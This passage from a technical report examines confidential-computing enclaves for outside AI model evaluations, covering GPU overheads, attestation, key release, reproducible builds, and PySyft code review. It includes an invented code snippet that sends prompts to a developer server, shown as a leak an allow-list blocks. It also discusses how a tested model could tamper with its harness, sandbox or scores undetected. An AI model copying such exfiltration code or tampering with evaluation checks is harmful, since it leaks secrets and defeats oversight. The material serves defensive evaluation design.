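Loading the weights is also slower. Yin and Wang measured transfers to a B300 at 55 gigabytes per second normally and 11 in confidential mode, so moving 16 gigabytes would take about a second and a half instead of a third of a second. The loading software can matter far more. A standard loader took 287 seconds to load a 120-billion-parameter model, and a tuned one took 8.4. At the standard loader's rate, the example model would take a little over a minute. Both loaders ran in confidential mode, so the 34-fold difference is mostly due to the loaders, although Yin and Wang list it among the losses that confidential mode causes.

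### What this adds to the cost of a test

Wang, Waqas and Smith (2026), in *Benchmarking Confidential GPU Inference on NVIDIA H100 under Intel TDX*, used the same type of Google Cloud machine as the 2026 Gemini pilot, with a single H100. Confidential mode reduced the throughput of Mistral-7B from 1,459 to 1,239 tokens per second. This is a 15 percent drop, but Wang and colleagues report 17.7 percent because they divide by the slower speed. Their figure is the right one for a budget because it is the increase in the time the same test takes, and rental charges rise in proportion. For a 30-billion-parameter model, the test would take 21.1 percent longer.

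At the Mistral speeds, 1,000 answers of 200 tokens would take 137 seconds normally and 161 seconds in confidential mode. The slowdown matters much more to a company serving customers all day than to an evaluator running one test.

Other measurements of the overhead vary. Trask and colleagues put it below 5 percent for the pilot's platform, but that figure comes from a 2023 source. *Confidential LLM Inference* reports losses of 4 to 8 percent on an H100. Nvidia's own tests of a 397-billion-parameter model on B300s show losses of 1.0 to 7.5 percent, with an average of about 4 percent, so Nvidia's advertised "98% of performance" is slightly high.

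Confidential mode slows inference most when the GPU handles one request at a time and nobody has tuned the software for that mode. Verma and Drean (2026), in *How does NVIDIA Confidential Computing impact inference and training performance?*, ran Kimi K2.6, a very large model, on eight B300s with vLLM. Confidential mode increased the time per token by 118 percent with a single short request and by 49 percent with 32 long ones. *EnclaveX* (2026) likewise found on an H200 that the penalty shrinks as the GPU handles more and longer requests together. An evaluator can therefore reduce the penalty by submitting all 1,000 prompts at once.

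Most of these figures come from companies with a commercial interest in the technology. Nvidia makes the GPUs, and Tinfoil, where Verma and Drean work, and Phala, where Yin and Wang work, both sell confidential computing platforms. But these companies also published some of the worst results, which makes their good ones easier to believe.

The checks that surround the test add little time. *OpenPcc* (2026) describes a system that adds attestation, an encrypted channel and tamper-proof logs to an enclave with an H100. With Llama 3 8B, these additions lengthened each request by less than a tenth of the GPU's computing time.

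### Working out whether the model fits

The weights need N × b / 8 bytes of memory, where N is the number of parameters and b is the number of bits per parameter. For the example model, this is 16 gigabytes. The table shows how many parameters would fill each GPU's memory.

| GPU | Memory | Parameters at 16 bits | Parameters at 8 bits |
|---|---|---|---|
| H100 | 80 GB | 40 billion | 80 billion |
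| H200 | 141 GB | 70 billion | 141 billion |
| B200 | 183 GB usable | 91 billion | 183 billion |
| B300 | about 287 GB | 143 billion | 287 billion |

Confidential mode itself takes very little of this memory. Asad and Grunseid found that it reserves 700 megabytes on a B200.

A model also needs working memory, mostly for the key-value cache, which stores the results of processing earlier tokens. Each token takes 2 × layers × key-value heads × head size × bytes per number. Llama 3 8B has 32 layers with 8 key-value heads of 128 numbers each, so at 16 bits a token takes 2 × 32 × 8 × 128 × 2 = 131,072 bytes. A prompt and answer totalling 1,000 tokens would need about 131 megabytes. After loading 16 gigabytes of weights, an H100 would have room for more than 400 such exchanges at once. The weights of a 40-billion-parameter model at 16 bits would fill the H100's memory, leaving no room for the cache.

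GLM-5.1, a model with about 744 billion parameters, needs about 744 gigabytes of memory at 8 bits per parameter. Eight H100s have only 640 gigabytes, but eight H200s have 1,128. At 16 bits the model would need 1,488 gigabytes and therefore eight B300s. Using fewer bits can change some of the model's answers, so the parties should test it at the precision the developer uses for its customers.

### Several GPUs and several machines

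The H100 and H200 support confidential work on several GPUs at once, but the host has to assign a whole group of connected GPUs to one customer, because these cards don't encrypt the traffic on NVLink, the fast connection between them. A customer who needs two GPUs may have to pay for eight. Cloud companies may offer less than the hardware allows. According to Google's documentation, as cited by Wang and colleagues, confidential work on an H100 requires a machine type with only one of these GPUs, so the pilot's set-up can't hold a model much above 30 billion parameters at 16 bits.

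The B200 and B300 encrypt NVLink traffic, and a confidential virtual machine can use one, two, four or eight of them. Yin and Wang ran two such machines side by side on one B300 server, and each could see only its own two GPUs. However, a program the host controls sets up the connections, and the customer cannot yet verify that program or its routes.

Splitting a model across more GPUs adds to the delay, because the GPUs must exchange partial results many times for each token. Asad and Grunseid ran a 229-billion-parameter model with tuned software and lost about 1.5 percent of throughput on four B200s and about 3 percent on eight. They attribute the loss to encrypting NVLink traffic. Verma and Drean found a delay of 9 to 13 microseconds per small exchange on Hopper GPUs, which don't encrypt that traffic, and 10 to 15 on Blackwell GPUs, which do. Encryption therefore can't explain most of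 the delay on small exchanges, and Verma and Drean suspect Nvidia's closed firmware. Either way, it makes sense to use the fewest GPUs that can hold the model.

A machine with eight B300s has about 2,290 gigabytes of memory, enough for the weights of a model with 1.1 trillion parameters at 16 bits. Pattern Labs and Anthropic say that the largest models in 2025 had up to a few trillion parameters, so some of them would need more than one machine. Neither Asad and Grunseid nor Yin and Wang measured confidential traffic between machines, which Asad and Grunseid expect to be a harder problem than traffic within one machine.

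Nvidia's newest system, Vera Rubin NVL72, avoids part of this problem by combining 72 GPUs and 36 processors in one rack. Nvidia says its confidential computing covers the whole rack, and VentureBeat describes it as the first system on this scale to encrypt all connections. SiliconANGLE (2026) reports the wider platform can also encrypt network traffic. According to GamesBeat's *Nvidia Vera Rubin ramps into full production for fall launch*, Microsoft Azure, CoreWeave and other cloud companies are adopting Nvidia's confidential computing. These are Nvidia's claims and press reports of them, so an evaluator planning a test in late 2026 has much better evidence about a single eight-GPU machine.

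### Reading the model's internals

Some evaluators want white-box access, including to activations, the intermediate numbers a model computes while producing an answer. In *Securing External Deeper-than-black-box GPAI Evaluations*, Tlaie and Farrell (2025) argue that outside evaluators need this access to find hidden risks. Pour Demain, a Brussels think tank where Farrell worked, has since tested white-box access to GLM-5.1 inside an enclave with eight H200s. The test used vllm-lens, a tool from the UK's AI Security Institute that copies activations as each layer runs. How much of this material may leave the enclave is a separate decision.

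In *Auditing a frontier model without seeing its weights*, McCann-Sayles and Verma (2026) report the results on behalf of Tinfoil, which supplied the platform. They say that confidential mode usually adds 5 to 7 percent to the running time, but added 33 to 38 percent with vllm-lens. They attribute the whole higher range to GLM-5.1, but their detailed results suggest otherwise. The times in seconds appear to come from another, unnamed model, and they give only percentages in brackets for GLM-5.1.

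| Set-up | Unnamed model, normal mode | Unnamed model, confidential mode | Increase, unnamed model | Increase, GLM-5.1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Standard vLLM with CUDA graphs | 0.445 s | 0.494 s | 11.1% | 6.7% |
| vLLM without CUDA graphs | 1.589 s | 2.114 s | 33.1% | not reported |
| vLLM with vllm-lens | 1.567 s | 2.168 s | 38.3% | 33.4% |

The increase was 33.4 percent for GLM-5.1 and 38 percent for the other model. Without the tool, GLM-5.1's slowdown was within the usual range of 5 to 7 percent, but the other model slowed by 11.1 percent. Two weeks later, Verma and Drean suggested that customers with busy machines plan for about 14 percent on Hopper and 25 to 30 percent on Blackwell, at least with untuned software.

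The percentages also understate how much reading a model's internals slows a run, because the runs they use as a baseline are already slow. For the unnamed model, vllm-lens in confidential mode took 2.168 seconds, about 4.9 times as long as the 0.445 seconds for standard vLLM in normal mode. About two-thirds of that increase has nothing to do with encryption, since vllm-lens took 1.567 seconds even in normal mode.

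The slowdown occurs because vllm-lens has to run its own code between the model's layers, which it can't do while the GPU replays a recorded sequence of commands. It therefore turns CUDA graphs off, and the processor goes back to sending commands separately. Turning CUDA graphs off without using vllm-lens raised the time almost as much. This agrees with Asad and Grunseid's synthetic test, where sending commands separately also caused most of the penalty from confidential computing.

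If the same ratio applied to the 8-billion-parameter model, a test that normally takes 137 seconds would take about 11 minutes, which is still short. For larger models or longer tests, McCann-Sayles and Verma suggest turning off the graphs only for the layers the evaluator wants to examine.

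## Checking the enclave and sending it the weights and tests

The cloud company that rents out the machine could be running any software on it, and neither the developer nor the evaluator can inspect it directly. Before the developer sends 16 gigabytes of weights and the evaluator sends 1,000 prompts, each needs evidence that a genuine enclave is running the program they agreed on, and that only this enclave can read what they send.

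### From start-up to a signed report

On an Intel TDX machine, the evidence builds up from the moment the virtual machine starts, as Eisoldt, Küchenmeister and colleagues explain in *SoK* (2025). The chip hashes the virtual machine's firmware and initial configuration and stores the result in a register that no software can change afterwards. The firmware then measures the operating system before starting it, and later layers can measure what they load in turn. These hashes go into four more registers. Software can add to them but can't overwrite them, because adding a component replaces the old value r with

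r′ = H(r ‖ H(component)),

where H is the hash function and ‖ joins two strings. The final value depends on every component and on the order in which they loaded.

On AMD's SEV-SNP, by contrast, the launch measurement often covers only the virtual firmware, so a host could swap the operating system without changing the measurement. Eisoldt and colleagues describe a fix, measured direct boot, which puts hashes of the operating system's core, start-up files and settings into the firmware before the chip measures the firmware. An evaluator therefore needs to know what a measurement covers as well as whether it matches the expected value.

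Once it is running, the enclave generates a public key pk and a private key that never leaves its memory. It then requests a report from the chip. Intel's and AMD's reports both have room for 64 bytes of data supplied by the enclave, and Trask and colleagues use this kind of field to tie the public key to the measurements. Each party also sends the enclave a nonce n, a random number used only once. To fit both the key and the nonce into the field, the enclave can enter their hash, H(pk ‖ n).

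The nonce prevents replay. Without it, a host could present an old report, and anyone who had since extracted that enclave's private key could read whatever was encrypted with the matching public key. Including the public key in the report prevents the host from substituting its own. If the report contained only a nonce, a dishonest host could pass the nonce to a genuine enclave elsewhere, get a fresh, genuine report, and present it alongside the host's own public key.

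*Session Attestation for Unmodified TLS Services in Confidential Virtual Machines* (2026) ties the report to a single connection. In TLS, the protocol that protects most web traffic, the server sends a temporary public value Y at the start of each connection. The report contains a hash of Y, the type of key exchange and a tag that marks the sender as the server. The client computes the same hash from its own connection, so a report made for any other connection fails the check.

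Finally, the report needs a signature. On TDX, a small separate enclave checks that the report comes from the same machine and signs it with an attestation key. A provisioning key, unique to the machine, certifies the attestation key, and Intel certifies the provisioning key. The verifier follows this chain from the report back to Intel's root certificate. If the machine has a confidential GPU, the verifier also needs the GPU's signed report.

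### An example with three failures

Here is an invented report for the example test, next to the evaluator's requirements. The hashes are shortened.

| Item | In the report | The evaluator requires |
|---|---|---|
| Enclave type | Intel TDX, debug mode off | Intel TDX, debug mode off |
| Chip firmware version | 7 | 7 or higher |
| Virtual firmware | 4be1…90c2 | 4be1…90c2 |
| Operating system | a07d…13f8 | a07d…13f8 |
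| Program that receives the weights and tests | c95e…6b04 | c95e…6b04 |
| Hash of public key and nonce | 18fa…d7e3 | H(pk ‖ n), using the nonce the evaluator has just sent |
| Signature | Valid, with a chain that ends at Intel | Valid, with a chain that ends at Intel |

Everything matches, so the evaluator can go ahead. Timings in *TEE Anchor* (Sakurai, 2026) imply that software can verify a TDX report in about 14 milliseconds.

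Now suppose the program's measurement comes back as 77d0…21ab. The host may have started a version that copies the prompts, or someone may have updated a harmless library. The evaluator can't tell which from the hash, because any change to the program produces an unrelated one. The evaluator should send nothing until somebody has explained the difference.

In another attempt, all the hashes match, but the chip is running old firmware, version 5. The chip is genuine and the program is correct, but the old firmware may contain a flaw that lets the host read the enclave's memory. The host can't report a higher version number to hide the old firmware, because the chip's signing key depends on the firmware version. Trask and colleagues recommend rejecting any firmware older than a set minimum version.

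A third report passes every check except the hash of the key and nonce, which was made with yesterday's nonce. The report is genuine, but the enclave it describes may no longer exist, so the evaluator rejects the report and asks for a new one.

The developer runs the same checks with its own nonce and gets its own report. The two parties should then compare public keys. If the keys match, both are dealing with the same enclave rather than two copies of the same program.

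A valid report does not show where the machine is, and someone who can open the machine has more ways to attack it. Sakurai proposes that the organisation running a data centre sign a certificate for each of its processors, based on the chip's unique identifier. A verifier can then confirm that a report comes from one of those machines. This check adds about 5 milliseconds.

### Releasing the weights

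Public-key encryption is slow for large files, so each sender generates a symmetric key, k, and encrypts the file with it. The sender then encrypts k with the enclave's public key and sends the encrypted file and the encrypted key. The evaluator can send the prompts this way as soon as the report passes.

The developer may prefer to put the encrypted weights near the machine in advance and, after the check, release only the key. Red Hat's *Enhancing AI inference security with confidential computing* (2025) describes such a design, which Red Hat is developing with Tinfoil. The developer packs the encrypted weights into a container image, the standard package for cloud software. The developer and the user who will supply data both attest the enclave before the developer releases the key.

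Pattern Labs and Anthropic describe how a key service releases the key to the weights. The enclave sends the service its signed report, which contains a temporary public key. The service verifies the report, uses the public key to encrypt the key to the weights, and sends the encrypted key back. Only the enclave has the private key needed to decrypt it.

The key service can run in three places. The cloud company's service is the most convenient, but anyone who takes over the developer's administrator account can rewrite the access rules and decrypt the weights, and the cloud company also has access. Running the service on the developer's own machine avoids this, but the developer must then write the software that checks the reports, which is easy to get wrong. The service can also run inside the enclave, so that the key never leaves it, but an enclave without permanent storage would have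 to stay switched on to keep the key. For a single test of the 8-billion-parameter model, the developer's own machine seems the best choice, because the developer can keep the service offline until the run begins and disconnect it afterwards.

Two mistakes can expose the weights despite these checks. If the key service accepts an enclave in debug mode, an attacker can watch the program as it handles the weights. If the developer retires an enclave program because of a security flaw but leaves its measurement on the approved list, an attacker can start the old program, exploit the flaw and get the key.

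### Where the expected values come from

The comparison of measurements is only as reliable as the list of expected values. If the evaluator just takes that list from the developer, a match shows that the enclave is running the program the developer intended, but not that this program was compiled from the source code the evaluator read. The developer could have added a few lines to that code before compiling it, so that the program copies the prompts.

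A reproducible build solves this because the evaluator, or someone it trusts, can rebuild the program and work out the expected values without the developer's help. Trask and colleagues point out that every honest person who rebuilds the program gets the same values, so one published mismatch is enough to expose a substitution.

Every stage of the build has to be reproducible. Pattern Labs and Anthropic list three stages: compiling the program, assembling the container image and packaging the enclave image. If a tool inserts the date at any stage, the final hash changes. As substitutes for a reproducible build, they suggest that experts use analysis tools to compare the finished program with the source code, or that the parties use a program that an outside organisation has built and others have already checked.

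Few enclaves meet this standard. *They don't care about this* (Wilde, Gutfleisch and colleagues, 2026) examined 115 deployments on Intel and AMD enclaves and found that 91 percent were not reproducible. In 80 percent, the operator left out the source code, a reference build to compare with, or both, so outsiders could not even try to reproduce the build. The operating system in the 2026 Gemini pilot is open source, but Trask and colleagues say that outsiders can't reproduce its individual builds because they take private signing keys as inputs.

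An attested build replaces the rebuilding with another enclave. A build program inside an enclave takes in the source code, compiles it and issues a signed report that links the two. In the version described by *Attestable Audit* (2026), a separate work from *Attestable Audits*, the public part of the report is

d = (H(source), H(build settings), measurement of the finished program).

The source code stays private, which would suit a developer with secret inference code. But the evaluator learns only that the program came from source code with a certain hash, so somebody it trusts still has to read that code and confirm the hash.

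*Kettle* (2026) describes a trade-off between reproducible builds, which require very little trust but take work to set up and repeat, and attested builds, which are easy to check but require trust in the chip maker. The build program also needs an expected measurement, so a verifier rebuilds that one program from public source and reuses the resulting measurement afterwards.

No method of this kind covers the chip's closed firmware, so the parties have to trust it. Trask and colleagues see some protection in every customer getting the same firmware, because the host then can't prepare a special version for one victim.

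### When a company's service does the checking

The parties can send the report to a verification service instead of verifying it themselves. The service checks the report and returns a signed statement that the enclave meets their policy. This saves them from writing the checks, but they have to rely on the company that runs the service. If that company also operates the machine, they are relying on it to check its own machine.

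According to Eisoldt and colleagues, Microsoft's attestation service runs in its own enclave and can attest itself, but its code is closed, so customers can only compare its measurement with a value from Microsoft. A customer can add a nonce to the service's statement to show that the statement is new. But the underlying report may be older, because Microsoft's software requests it when the virtual machine starts and keeps a copy. Customers can choose another verifier, but they would receive the same stored copy.

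Customers who do the checks independently still have to trust the cloud company. Eisoldt and colleagues compared four types of confidential virtual machine in early 2025, and none let the customer verify all the software.

| Service | Source of the report | Can customers rebuild the virtual firmware? | What measures the operating system? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Microsoft Azure, AMD | Stored copy in Microsoft's software | No | Closed Microsoft software |
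| Amazon Web Services, AMD | Directly from the chip | Yes | Nothing inside the virtual machine |
| Google Cloud, AMD | Directly from the chip | No | Nothing inside the virtual machine |
| Google Cloud, Intel | Directly from the chip | No | Closed Google firmware |

Some of this may have changed, since Microsoft was already developing an open version of its software. Eisoldt and colleagues conclude that, strictly speaking, these services defeat the purpose of confidential computing. That is too harsh for many evaluations, in which the developer and the evaluator mainly distrust each other and regard the cloud company as neutral, a situation they also recognise. But their criticism holds when the cloud company belongs to one of the two sides, as in the 2026 pilot, where Google's services signed and verified the report on a test of Google's own model.

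### Attestable Audits

*Attestable Audits*, by Christoph Schnabl and three colleagues at the University of Cambridge, turns these parts into a complete procedure for testing a model. It sets six goals:

1. The report identifies the model by hashes of its weights and code.
2. The report ties the result to an approved version of the test.
3. The weights and the test set stay secret.
4. Anyone can look up the hashes of the enclave's software, the model and the test, and can repeat the steps that built the software.
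5. Nothing from one session remains in the enclave for the next.
6. A user who later talks to the model can confirm that its answers come from the tested model.

The design assumes attackers who can intercept network traffic or who control the machine, but not attackers who merely want to stop the test.

It has three protocols. Below, M is the model, Q is a compressed copy of it, C is the evaluation code, T is the test set and R is the result. Enc(k, x) is x encrypted with key k, and Att(x) is a signed report that contains the enclave's measurements and x. Anyone sending encrypted data first checks the enclave's report and then sends k encrypted with pk.

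The *prepare* protocol is optional. It makes a smaller copy of the model by storing each weight in fewer bits, a process called quantisation.

1. The enclave generates a key pair and publishes Att(pk).
2. The developer sends Enc(k, M).
3. The enclave decrypts M and computes Q.
4. It publishes Att(H(M), H(Q)), returns Enc(k, Q) to the developer and shuts down.

The report shows that Q came from M. The Cambridge group treats testing Q as a valid approximation to testing M, but the report can't show this, because quantisation may change some answers.

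The *audit* protocol runs the test in a new enclave.

1. The enclave generates a new key pair and publishes Att(pk).
2. The developer sends Enc(k₁, Q), and the evaluator sends Enc(k₂, C and T).
3. The enclave decrypts everything and runs C on Q and T in a sandbox, a closed-off area from which the code can't reach the rest of the enclave.
4. It publishes R and Att(H(Q), H(C and T), H(R)), then shuts down.

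An implementation should follow the paper's text rather than its printed listings. The audit listing leaves R out of the signed report, so someone could present a different score alongside a genuine report. The prepare listing encrypts Q with the wrong value, which has already been sent over the network, so an eavesdropper could decrypt the model. Both look like slips, since the text describes the steps correctly. The paper also explicitly omits replay protection, so a real system would need to add the nonce.

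The *inference* protocol is for people who use the model later.

1. A new enclave downloads the earlier reports and publishes Att(pk, earlier reports).
2. The developer sends Enc(k, M), and the enclave stops if H(M) differs from the hash in those reports.
3. The user sends an encrypted prompt p, and the model produces an answer x.
4. The enclave returns x and Att(H(M), p, x, R), both encrypted.

The user now has signed evidence that connects the answer to a model and its test result, and can show it to a regulator if the answer suggests that the test missed something.

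All the public reports go into a transparency log, a record that people outside the test can consult. Such logs normally allow new entries but no deletions. If a developer tested 27 variants on the same 1,000 prompts and every run reached the log, it would show 27 different model hashes beside the same test hash. The host could keep a run out of the log by cutting the enclave's connection, and the design doesn't try to stop this, so a missing entry doesn't prove that no test was run.

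The prototype runs on Nitro Enclaves, so Amazon both makes the protection and hosts it. The Cambridge group suggests repeating the test on enclaves from several manufacturers, so readers can choose which report to believe. This makes the result more credible but puts the secrets at greater risk, because a flaw in any enclave could leak them.

### The prototype's results and costs

The Cambridge group tested Llama-3.1-8B, which has as many parameters as the example model. They stored its weights at 4 bits each, reducing them from 16 gigabytes to roughly 4. They gave it 500 prompts from each of three benchmarks: XSum, which asks for short summaries; MMLU, the multiple-choice exam; and ToxicChat, which contains messages that may provoke toxic answers. For comparison, they ran the 4-bit model on ordinary processors and the 16-bit model on an Nvidia L40S GPU, both without an enclave.

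| | Enclave, 4 cores | Ordinary processor, 4 cores | Ordinary processor, 8 cores | L40S GPU, 16-bit model |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Price per hour | $0.38 | $0.19 | $0.38 | $0.89 |
| Tokens per second | 1.84 | 2.04 | 3.54 | 202 |
| Price per 100,000 tokens | $5.80 | $2.61 | $3.01 | $0.12 |
| Similarity to reference summaries (1 is best) | 0.47 | 0.50 | 0.49 | 0.58 |
| Toxic answers | 2.4% | 2.0% | 1.7% | 2.6% |
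| MMLU accuracy | 51.4% | 52.6% | 48.6% | 58.9% |

The price per 100,000 tokens follows from the first two rows:

price = hourly price × 100,000 / (3,600 × tokens per second).

By this measure, the enclave costs 5.80 / 2.61 = 2.2 times as much as the ordinary processor with the same number of cores. Most of the difference arises because part of the machine has to stay outside the enclave, so the enclave needs a machine that costs twice as much per hour. Encryption explains little of the difference, since the enclave is only 10 percent slower.

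The enclave costs about 48 times as much as the GPU ($5.80 compared with $0.12) and is about 110 times slower. *Attestable Audits* gives the cost ratio as 21.7, but that figure is the ordinary processor's cost, $2.61, divided by the GPU's $0.12.

The difference in cost is small. If the example model wrote 1,000 answers of 200 tokens each, the run would cost about $11.60 in the enclave and $0.24 on the GPU. Time is the bigger problem, because the run would take about 30 hours in the enclave and 17 minutes on the GPU. Copying the model into the enclave adds at most two minutes.

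A confidential GPU would remove most of this gap. The Cambridge group expected it to reduce the overhead to perhaps 5 times. That estimate looks too pessimistic given the H100 tests by Wang and colleagues.

The scores suggest that the enclave doesn't affect the answers. The three 4-bit runs differ by up to 4 points on MMLU, but with 500 questions each score has a standard error of about 2.2 points, so chance could easily explain the difference. The GPU scored higher because it ran the model at 16 bits and with a different limit on text length, and because the enclave's model often gave answers that the scoring program couldn't read. Without those answers, the accuracy of the enclave's model rises from 51.4 to 57.4 percent.

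In a separate comparison outside the enclave, the 4-bit version scored 56.2 percent and the 8-bit version 57.5 percent, counting only the questions each answered readably. Of the 500 ToxicChat prompts, the 4-bit version gave toxic answers to 12 and the 8-bit version to 11. So for this model 4 bits seem nearly as good as 8, but a difference of one toxic answer is weak evidence of how quantisation affects safety.

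### What attestation misses after start-up

Attestation records what the machine loaded but not everything that happens afterwards. Mao and Chang (2026), in *PS-UIE*, explain that after the verifier has checked a virtual machine, it can still load more parts of its operating system, start new programs and bring new code into memory. *Two-Way Confidential VMs (2cVM)* (2026) also notes that this limits what a launch measurement can establish about a full virtual machine. The problem is smaller for an enclave with one fixed program that loads all its code at the start.

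Trask and colleagues give the example of an enclave that runs a server for remote logins. An administrator could log in and change the code after an outside party has received the signed hash. They propose leaving such services out of the software, so that the program the parties have checked offers no way to alter it.

This example counts against a suggestion they make later in the same paper. They speculate that in future tests of advanced models' hacking skills, if a model tried to change its weights, its sandbox or its harness (the code that runs the test), the enclave's hash would no longer match and the machine would stop at once. But if an administrator can change the code without affecting a hash that the chip has already signed, a model can too. Nothing in the procedure they describe measures the software again during the test or stops the machine when it changes. The problem is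 even clearer for the weights, which arrive after start-up and so were never included in the start-up measurement.

A model also needs a way to change the harness. In the example, the evaluation code only reads and scores the text that the 8-billion-parameter model writes, so the model would have to exploit a bug. A test of hacking skills usually lets the model run commands, which gives it many more opportunities.

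Engineers could build part of what Trask and colleagues have in mind. Mao and Chang's system adds a monitor to an AMD virtual machine, at a privilege level above the operating system. Before a program file or code library runs, the monitor hashes it, compares the hash with a list of rules and can block it. It also keeps a protected log that a verifier can check later.

The system checks files that the processor executes directly, so it would catch a model that installed a new program. But it would miss some of the changes that matter most. A model could alter the weights, which are numbers, or a harness written in Python, which is a text file that another program reads, without triggering a check. The system also works only on AMD processors, while the 2026 pilot used Intel's.

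A second signed report, with new hashes of the weights and the harness taken at the end of the run, would reveal any lasting change. It would not reveal whether the model had altered its scores and then restored the original files. The model would also have to be unable to tamper with the program that calculates the hashes.

It is safer to keep the model away from the harness in the first place. The sandbox in *Attestable Audits* holds the model and the evaluation code together, so it protects the rest of the enclave from both but doesn't protect the evaluation code from the model. If the model can run commands, the evaluator should give it a separate sandbox and keep the scoring code and the record of the model's answers outside it.

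## Agreeing on code that neither side fully sees

Attestation shows which program is running in the enclave, but that program could leak secrets even if the enclave works correctly. Before sending the 1,000 prompts, the evaluator needs reason to believe that no code in the enclave will pass them on. The developer needs the same assurance that the evaluation code won't leak the 16 gigabytes of weights it will run alongside.

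### When both sides can read all the code

The problem is easy if both sides are willing to show their code. Trask and colleagues illustrate this with the Millionaire's Problem, in which two people want to know who is richer without revealing their bank balances. One of them starts an enclave running an open-source program that accepts two numbers, outputs which is larger, deletes everything and shuts down. Both read the program, check that the enclave's report matches it, and send in their balances.

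In some model tests, only the model is secret. *ManaTEE*, by Sun and Choi, describes an open-source system, begun at TikTok, in which a model's owner and an outside partner agree on a test program such as the public lm-evaluation-harness. The enclave runs the program and signs the result together with hashes of the model and the program. Sun and Choi say that even a malicious program could not get the model out. That may be true of leaks through the network or the disk, but a malicious program could still put pieces of the model into the result, so both sides have to read the program before they agree to it.

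Reading the enclave's code properly takes some skill. *Sharing without Showing* (2024) presents a system in which the data supplier has to check that the code can't leak private keys and that it combines the data thoroughly enough for the result to be safe to release. The paper suggests that software could do part of this work, for example by tracking where each piece of data flows.

A safety test is harder because the inference code and the scoring method may both be secret. Each side then has to approve a program that it can't fully read.

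### Structured transparency

PySyft, an open-source library from the non-profit OpenMined, organises this approval. It builds on structured transparency, a 2020 framework that responds to what OpenMined's *Syft Code Policies* calls the copy problem. Once an owner releases data, the owner can no longer control how others use or share it. The data that answers a question also tends to come with other information that somebody could misuse. Under the framework, the parties agree on one precise flow of information instead of handing over the data.

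Such an agreement has five parts. Input privacy keeps the weights and prompts hidden, and input verification lets both sides confirm that the right ones were used. Output privacy limits what the result reveals, and output verification lets the recipient confirm that the result is genuine. Flow governance determines who can change any of this. In the example, the enclave's encryption provides input privacy, and hashes of the weights and the test set provide input verification. The release rule provides output privacy, and the signature on the score provides output verification. PySyft handles governance by running code only if both parties have approved it.

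### From mock assets to shutdown

A PySyft test begins when one party rents the enclave and starts it with PySyft inside. That party can switch the enclave off but, according to Trask and colleagues, has no other privileges. Both parties check the attestation report.

Each party must then write code for something it can't see. OpenMined's *PySyft used for first double-blind evaluation of a proprietary, frontier-class AI model* lists this among several everyday problems that academic work on privacy has largely overlooked. PySyft handles this with mock assets. The developer might upload a tiny model with random weights that takes in and returns text in the same way as the real one. The evaluator might upload ten harmless prompts in the format of the real 1,000. Each side downloads the other's mock and works on its own code until it runs. If the model has a standard interface, the developer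 can name the interface instead of uploading a mock.

Trying code on mock data can confirm that it runs, but not that the test is any good. In a demonstration with OpenMined, the research group EleutherAI hosted a private collection of more than 200,000 training documents, and an outside evaluator searched it for mentions of three fairly harmless biological agents. The evaluator wrote a keyword search using mock data. EleutherAI reviewed the search, ran it on the real documents, inspected the roughly 60 it flagged, and released only a summary. For a soil bacterium, 79 percent of the flagged documents were correct matches, but for RSV, a respiratory virus, only 11 percent were.

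No one could have predicted those figures from mock data, and EleutherAI could calculate them only because it knew which documents were dangerous. EleutherAI advises evaluators to measure how well a method works before they run it remotely. The same advice applies to scoring the 1,000 prompts in *Attestable Audits*, where the scoring program often failed to read the model's answers. A mock model with tidy answers would not have exposed that problem.

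When the code is ready, its author submits it with policies that the system enforces. Trask, Yesilyurt and colleagues divide these into input, output and run-time policies in *Secure Enclaves for AI Evaluation*. An input policy names the assets that the code may use. For instance, PySyft's ExactMatch policy ties the approved code to one model or test set, so nobody can reuse the approval on another. An output policy controls which results are returned and how often. One built-in policy allows a single run, and a custom one in OpenMined's documentation allows ten. A run-time policy sets conditions for running the code, such as who may start it.

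These limits would make it harder for a developer to test 27 variants and publish the best score. If the approval covers one run on one set of weights, the developer needs the evaluator's consent to test each further variant.

But they don't replace reading the code. A limit on the number of runs doesn't restrict what each run reveals. The function in OpenMined's ten-run demonstration returns its input unchanged, which is harmless for a list of three numbers but would expose a model's weights in a single run. OpenMined says that users can write stricter policies, such as one that releases only aggregated results, but PySyft doesn't supply them by default and manual review remains necessary.

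Each party then reviews the other's code, and PySyft runs nothing until both approve. In the 2024 trial, the reviewers signed all the code without seeing the weights or the prompts, and they could consult a shared log of every action. They could also see the model's whole architecture. This did no harm because the model was GPT-2, which is public, but a commercial developer might well object to revealing its own. After approval, PySyft runs the code on the real assets and sends the result to one party or both, as agreed. The enclave then deletes whatever remains and shuts down.

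### Redaction with an allow-list

Redaction lets a party hide parts of the code that it submits for review. Trask and colleagues note that a secret program is built from functions, which are built from smaller functions, until the pieces are too basic to be secret. A confidential model architecture, for example, is a secret arrangement of additions, multiplications and similar steps from open-source libraries such as PyTorch and JAX. If none of those steps can send data out of the enclave, or write it to a place from which something else would send it, no arrangement of them can either.

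The parties therefore agree on an allow-list of such steps. A tool called syft-restrict checks the hidden lines and provides an attestation that they call nothing else. Here is an invented piece of the developer's inference code:

```python
def answer(prompt, weights):
    x = embed(prompt, weights)
    # hidden part begins
    x = torch.matmul(x, weights["layer_1"])         # accepted
    requests.post(DEVELOPER_SERVER, data=prompt)    # refused
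    # hidden part ends
    return to_text(x)
```

The evaluator sees all the code except the hidden part. `torch.matmul` is on the list of allowed functions because it only multiplies two grids of numbers. `requests.post` sends data over the network, so it is not on the list, and any code that calls it fails the check. The developer has to remove the call before the evaluator will approve anything. An evaluator can hide its scoring method in the same way, with a list that might contain comparisons, counts and averages.

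The list has to name individual functions, because PyTorch also includes functions that save files, download models and send data to other machines. The check has to cover code that reassigns names as well as function calls, because Python lets a running program change what a name refers to. A hidden line could make `torch.matmul` refer to `requests.post`, and a checker that only compared names would approve the leak.

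The argument fails when the basic steps themselves are secret. Large developers write their own GPU routines for speed, and an evaluator can't tell what a secret routine does from its name. Partly for this reason, some of Google's code went into the 2026 pilot unreviewed, with the evaluator's consent.

### What gets past the list

An allow-list stops an obvious attempt to send out the prompts or save them to a file. It also stops accidental leaks, such as those from a logging line a programmer forgot to delete.

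Listing functions doesn't help if one of them is faulty. A caller can sometimes use a malformed input to make a library run the caller's own code, and even widely used libraries have many faults. Anthropic had its models look for 21 known bugs in older versions of the SQLite database and three libraries for images and compression. According to Help Net Security's *Anthropic's AI bug tests uncover previously undisclosed flaws* (2026), the models also found 316 other bugs. Maintainers had already fixed or knew about 189 of these, which left 127 for Anthropic to report. An AI judge confirmed the findings, so some may be wrong, and most probably wouldn't let anyone steal a prompt. But PyTorch is much larger than any of these four projects, so it may have more bugs.

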